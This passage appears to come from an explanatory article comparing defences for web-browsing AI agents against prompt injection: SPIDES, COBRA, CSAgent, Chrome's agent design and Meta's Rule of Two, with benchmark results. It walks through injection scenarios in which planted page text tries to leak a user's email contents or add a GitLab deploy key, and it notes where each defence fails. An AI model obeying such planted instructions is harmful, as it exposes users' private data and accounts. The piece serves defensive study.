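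A browser agent could show the planner the trustworthy parts of a page and hide the rest. *SPIDES* (Zverev, Kim and colleagues, 2026) does this with labels that a site's operator adds to individual page elements. A shop would mark its own product descriptions as trusted, customer reviews as untrusted, and a saved card number as readable only by the user and the shop. The user lists the sites whose operators they trust, and SPIDES treats everything from other sites as untrusted and public.

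If Ben's mail provider has labeled an email as readable only by him, SPIDES will not send its contents to the pharmacy without his approval, whatever the pharmacy claims about its own page.

The researchers tested SPIDES on 28 linked websites they had built, with 56 ordinary tasks and 56 attacks. As a worst case, they let the attacker dictate the model's output whenever it had read untrusted text. SPIDES blocked every attack, while 53.2% to 73.2% succeeded against SOPGuard, depending on the model. SPIDES completed 67.1% to 86.1% of the ordinary tasks.

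Those test sites were correctly labeled throughout, but real websites are not. On a site the user trusts, SPIDES treats an element as trusted and public if neither it nor the elements around it has a label. If a shop forgets to label its reviews, SPIDES will show them to the planner as the shop's own words. If a mail provider forgets to label a message, SPIDES will allow the message's contents to be sent anywhere.

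### Fixing the rules before the task begins

A policy can also use the user's request without tracking where every word came from. Before the agent reads any page, the software lists the sites the task needs and blocks all others until the task is over. For Ben's question, the list would include the pharmacy but not his webmail. The planted instruction would fail when the agent tried to open his mail, before it had anything to leak.

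Zingrillo, Foerster and colleagues (2026), in *Securing Computer-Use Agents Against Branch Steering Attacks*, built this into a system called COBRA. Its list contains the sites that the user's request marks as trusted, plus common infrastructure that pages need to load. A proxy enforces the list, and nothing the agent reads can extend it. In 21 test cases where an injection tried to make an unauthorised web request, all the requests succeeded without the proxy and none with it.

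The list cannot stop an attack that stays on a permitted site. On WASP, a benchmark with simulated GitLab and Reddit sites, the list blocked all 5 attacks that crossed to another site and none of the 14 that stayed on the same site. In one of those 14, the user wanted to comment on a GitLab issue, and the injection tried to add a deploy key, which gives its holder access to the code.

COBRA blocked those 14 too once it had a sitemap, which describes the operations a site offers and the requests that perform them. With a sitemap, the proxy can allow the request that posts a comment and refuse the one that adds a key. *ceLLMate* (2025) had introduced sitemaps of this kind for browser agents, which each site's developers were meant to write, but few sites have a reason to publish one yet. Zingrillo and colleagues generated sitemaps by crawling, and these contained every operation needed for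 about 70% of the web tasks they checked.

COBRA also fixes limits for each branch of its plan, such as which sites that branch may contact. On the researchers' own benchmark, branch steering succeeded in 89.5% of cases against a plain planner-and-reader design and in none against COBRA.

Planning without seeing the screen still reduces the number of tasks completed. With Claude Sonnet 5 both planning and reading the screen, and up to five attempts per task, COBRA completed 38.8% of 361 computer tasks, compared with 51.0% for the same model without the separation. On the 46 tasks that used the Chrome browser, COBRA completed 15, compared with 20 without the separation. This setup cost $0.627 per task. Using GPT-5 to plan and a small open model to read the screen cost $0.332 per task and completed 36.8%.

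Checking each action against rules written in advance can add much less overhead. *Secure and Efficient Access Control for Computer-Use Agents via Context Space* (2025) describes CSAgent, which prepares its policies during an application's development and needs one extra model call per task. It slowed agents by less than 5% on two benchmarks and by 48% on AgentDojo. It used between 7% and 200% more tokens, with the smallest increase on the most complex tasks.

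None of this helps much when the request names no site. The software can't build a list from the earlier question about a washing machine's error code, and if the agent may add sites to the list as it reads, an attacker can influence which ones it adds.

Google's design for Chrome deals with this by letting the agent propose new sites and having a separate model approve them. *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome* (Parker, 2025) describes two lists of sites for each task. The agent may only read sites on the first list, but may also click and type on sites on the second. The approving model does not see web content, so planted text cannot reach it directly. Chrome also hides embedded frames from the agent if they come from unlisted sites, and lets the agent open URLs it wrote itself only if they are known and public.

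If Ben's agent proposed opening his mail to answer a question about delivery, the approving model should refuse. But the model can misjudge in a way that a fixed list cannot. When Ana asks about the medicine in her doctor's email, both her mail and the pharmacy belong on the lists. A planted instruction could then try to make the agent type other parts of her mail into the pharmacy's search box. Chrome has a second model, also shielded from web content, that vetoes actions unrelated to the user's goal. That model receives only a description of the proposed action, so it may not detect that the text came from an unrelated email.

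Chrome's design is the only one described here that was built for a mass-market product. CaMeL, FIDES, PRUDENTIA, SOPGuard, SPIDES, ceLLMate, COBRA and CSAgent were all published as research systems. By December 2025, Google had implemented a simpler version of Chrome's design that tracked only the list of sites where the agent may act. Parker gives no figures for attacks stopped or for tasks the agent could no longer complete.

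### Browsing without private data

The simplest use of provenance is to give no private data to an agent that reads the open web. The policy then does not need to determine where a fetch came from, because even an injected fetch cannot leak private data the agent doesn't have.

Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) turns this into general guidance for developers. It widens two of the three conditions in Willison's trifecta. Access to private data now also covers access to sensitive systems, and external communication now also covers actions that change something, such as making a payment. An agent should meet at most two of the three conditions in any session. If a task needs all three, a person or another reliable check should supervise the agent.

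Meta's example research assistant can read untrusted pages and contact any site, but it gives up access to private data. It runs in a sandboxed browser with no saved logins and knows little about the user beyond the request. In such a session, Ben's agent could not open his mail, so the pharmacy would learn nothing about his medicine. Ana could still ask for the price of metformin, but if the drug's name were in her doctor's email, she would have to look it up and type it herself.

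Logging out of websites is not enough if private data reaches the agent another way, as it did through Claude's memory feature in the Memory Heist. The request can also be private, as Ana's is, and Meta advises telling users how the agent might share it. Developers can apply the same principle to part of a product, as OpenAI does by removing setup secrets from the cloud version of Codex.

Meta also allows an agent to change modes once during a session. It can browse freely at first, then lose its ability to communicate before it gains access to private data. For example, an agent could read a country's visa rules and then check the user's documents against them. The order cannot be reversed. If an agent has to read a doctor's letter to know which illness to research, it would need a new session in which the user supplies the search term.
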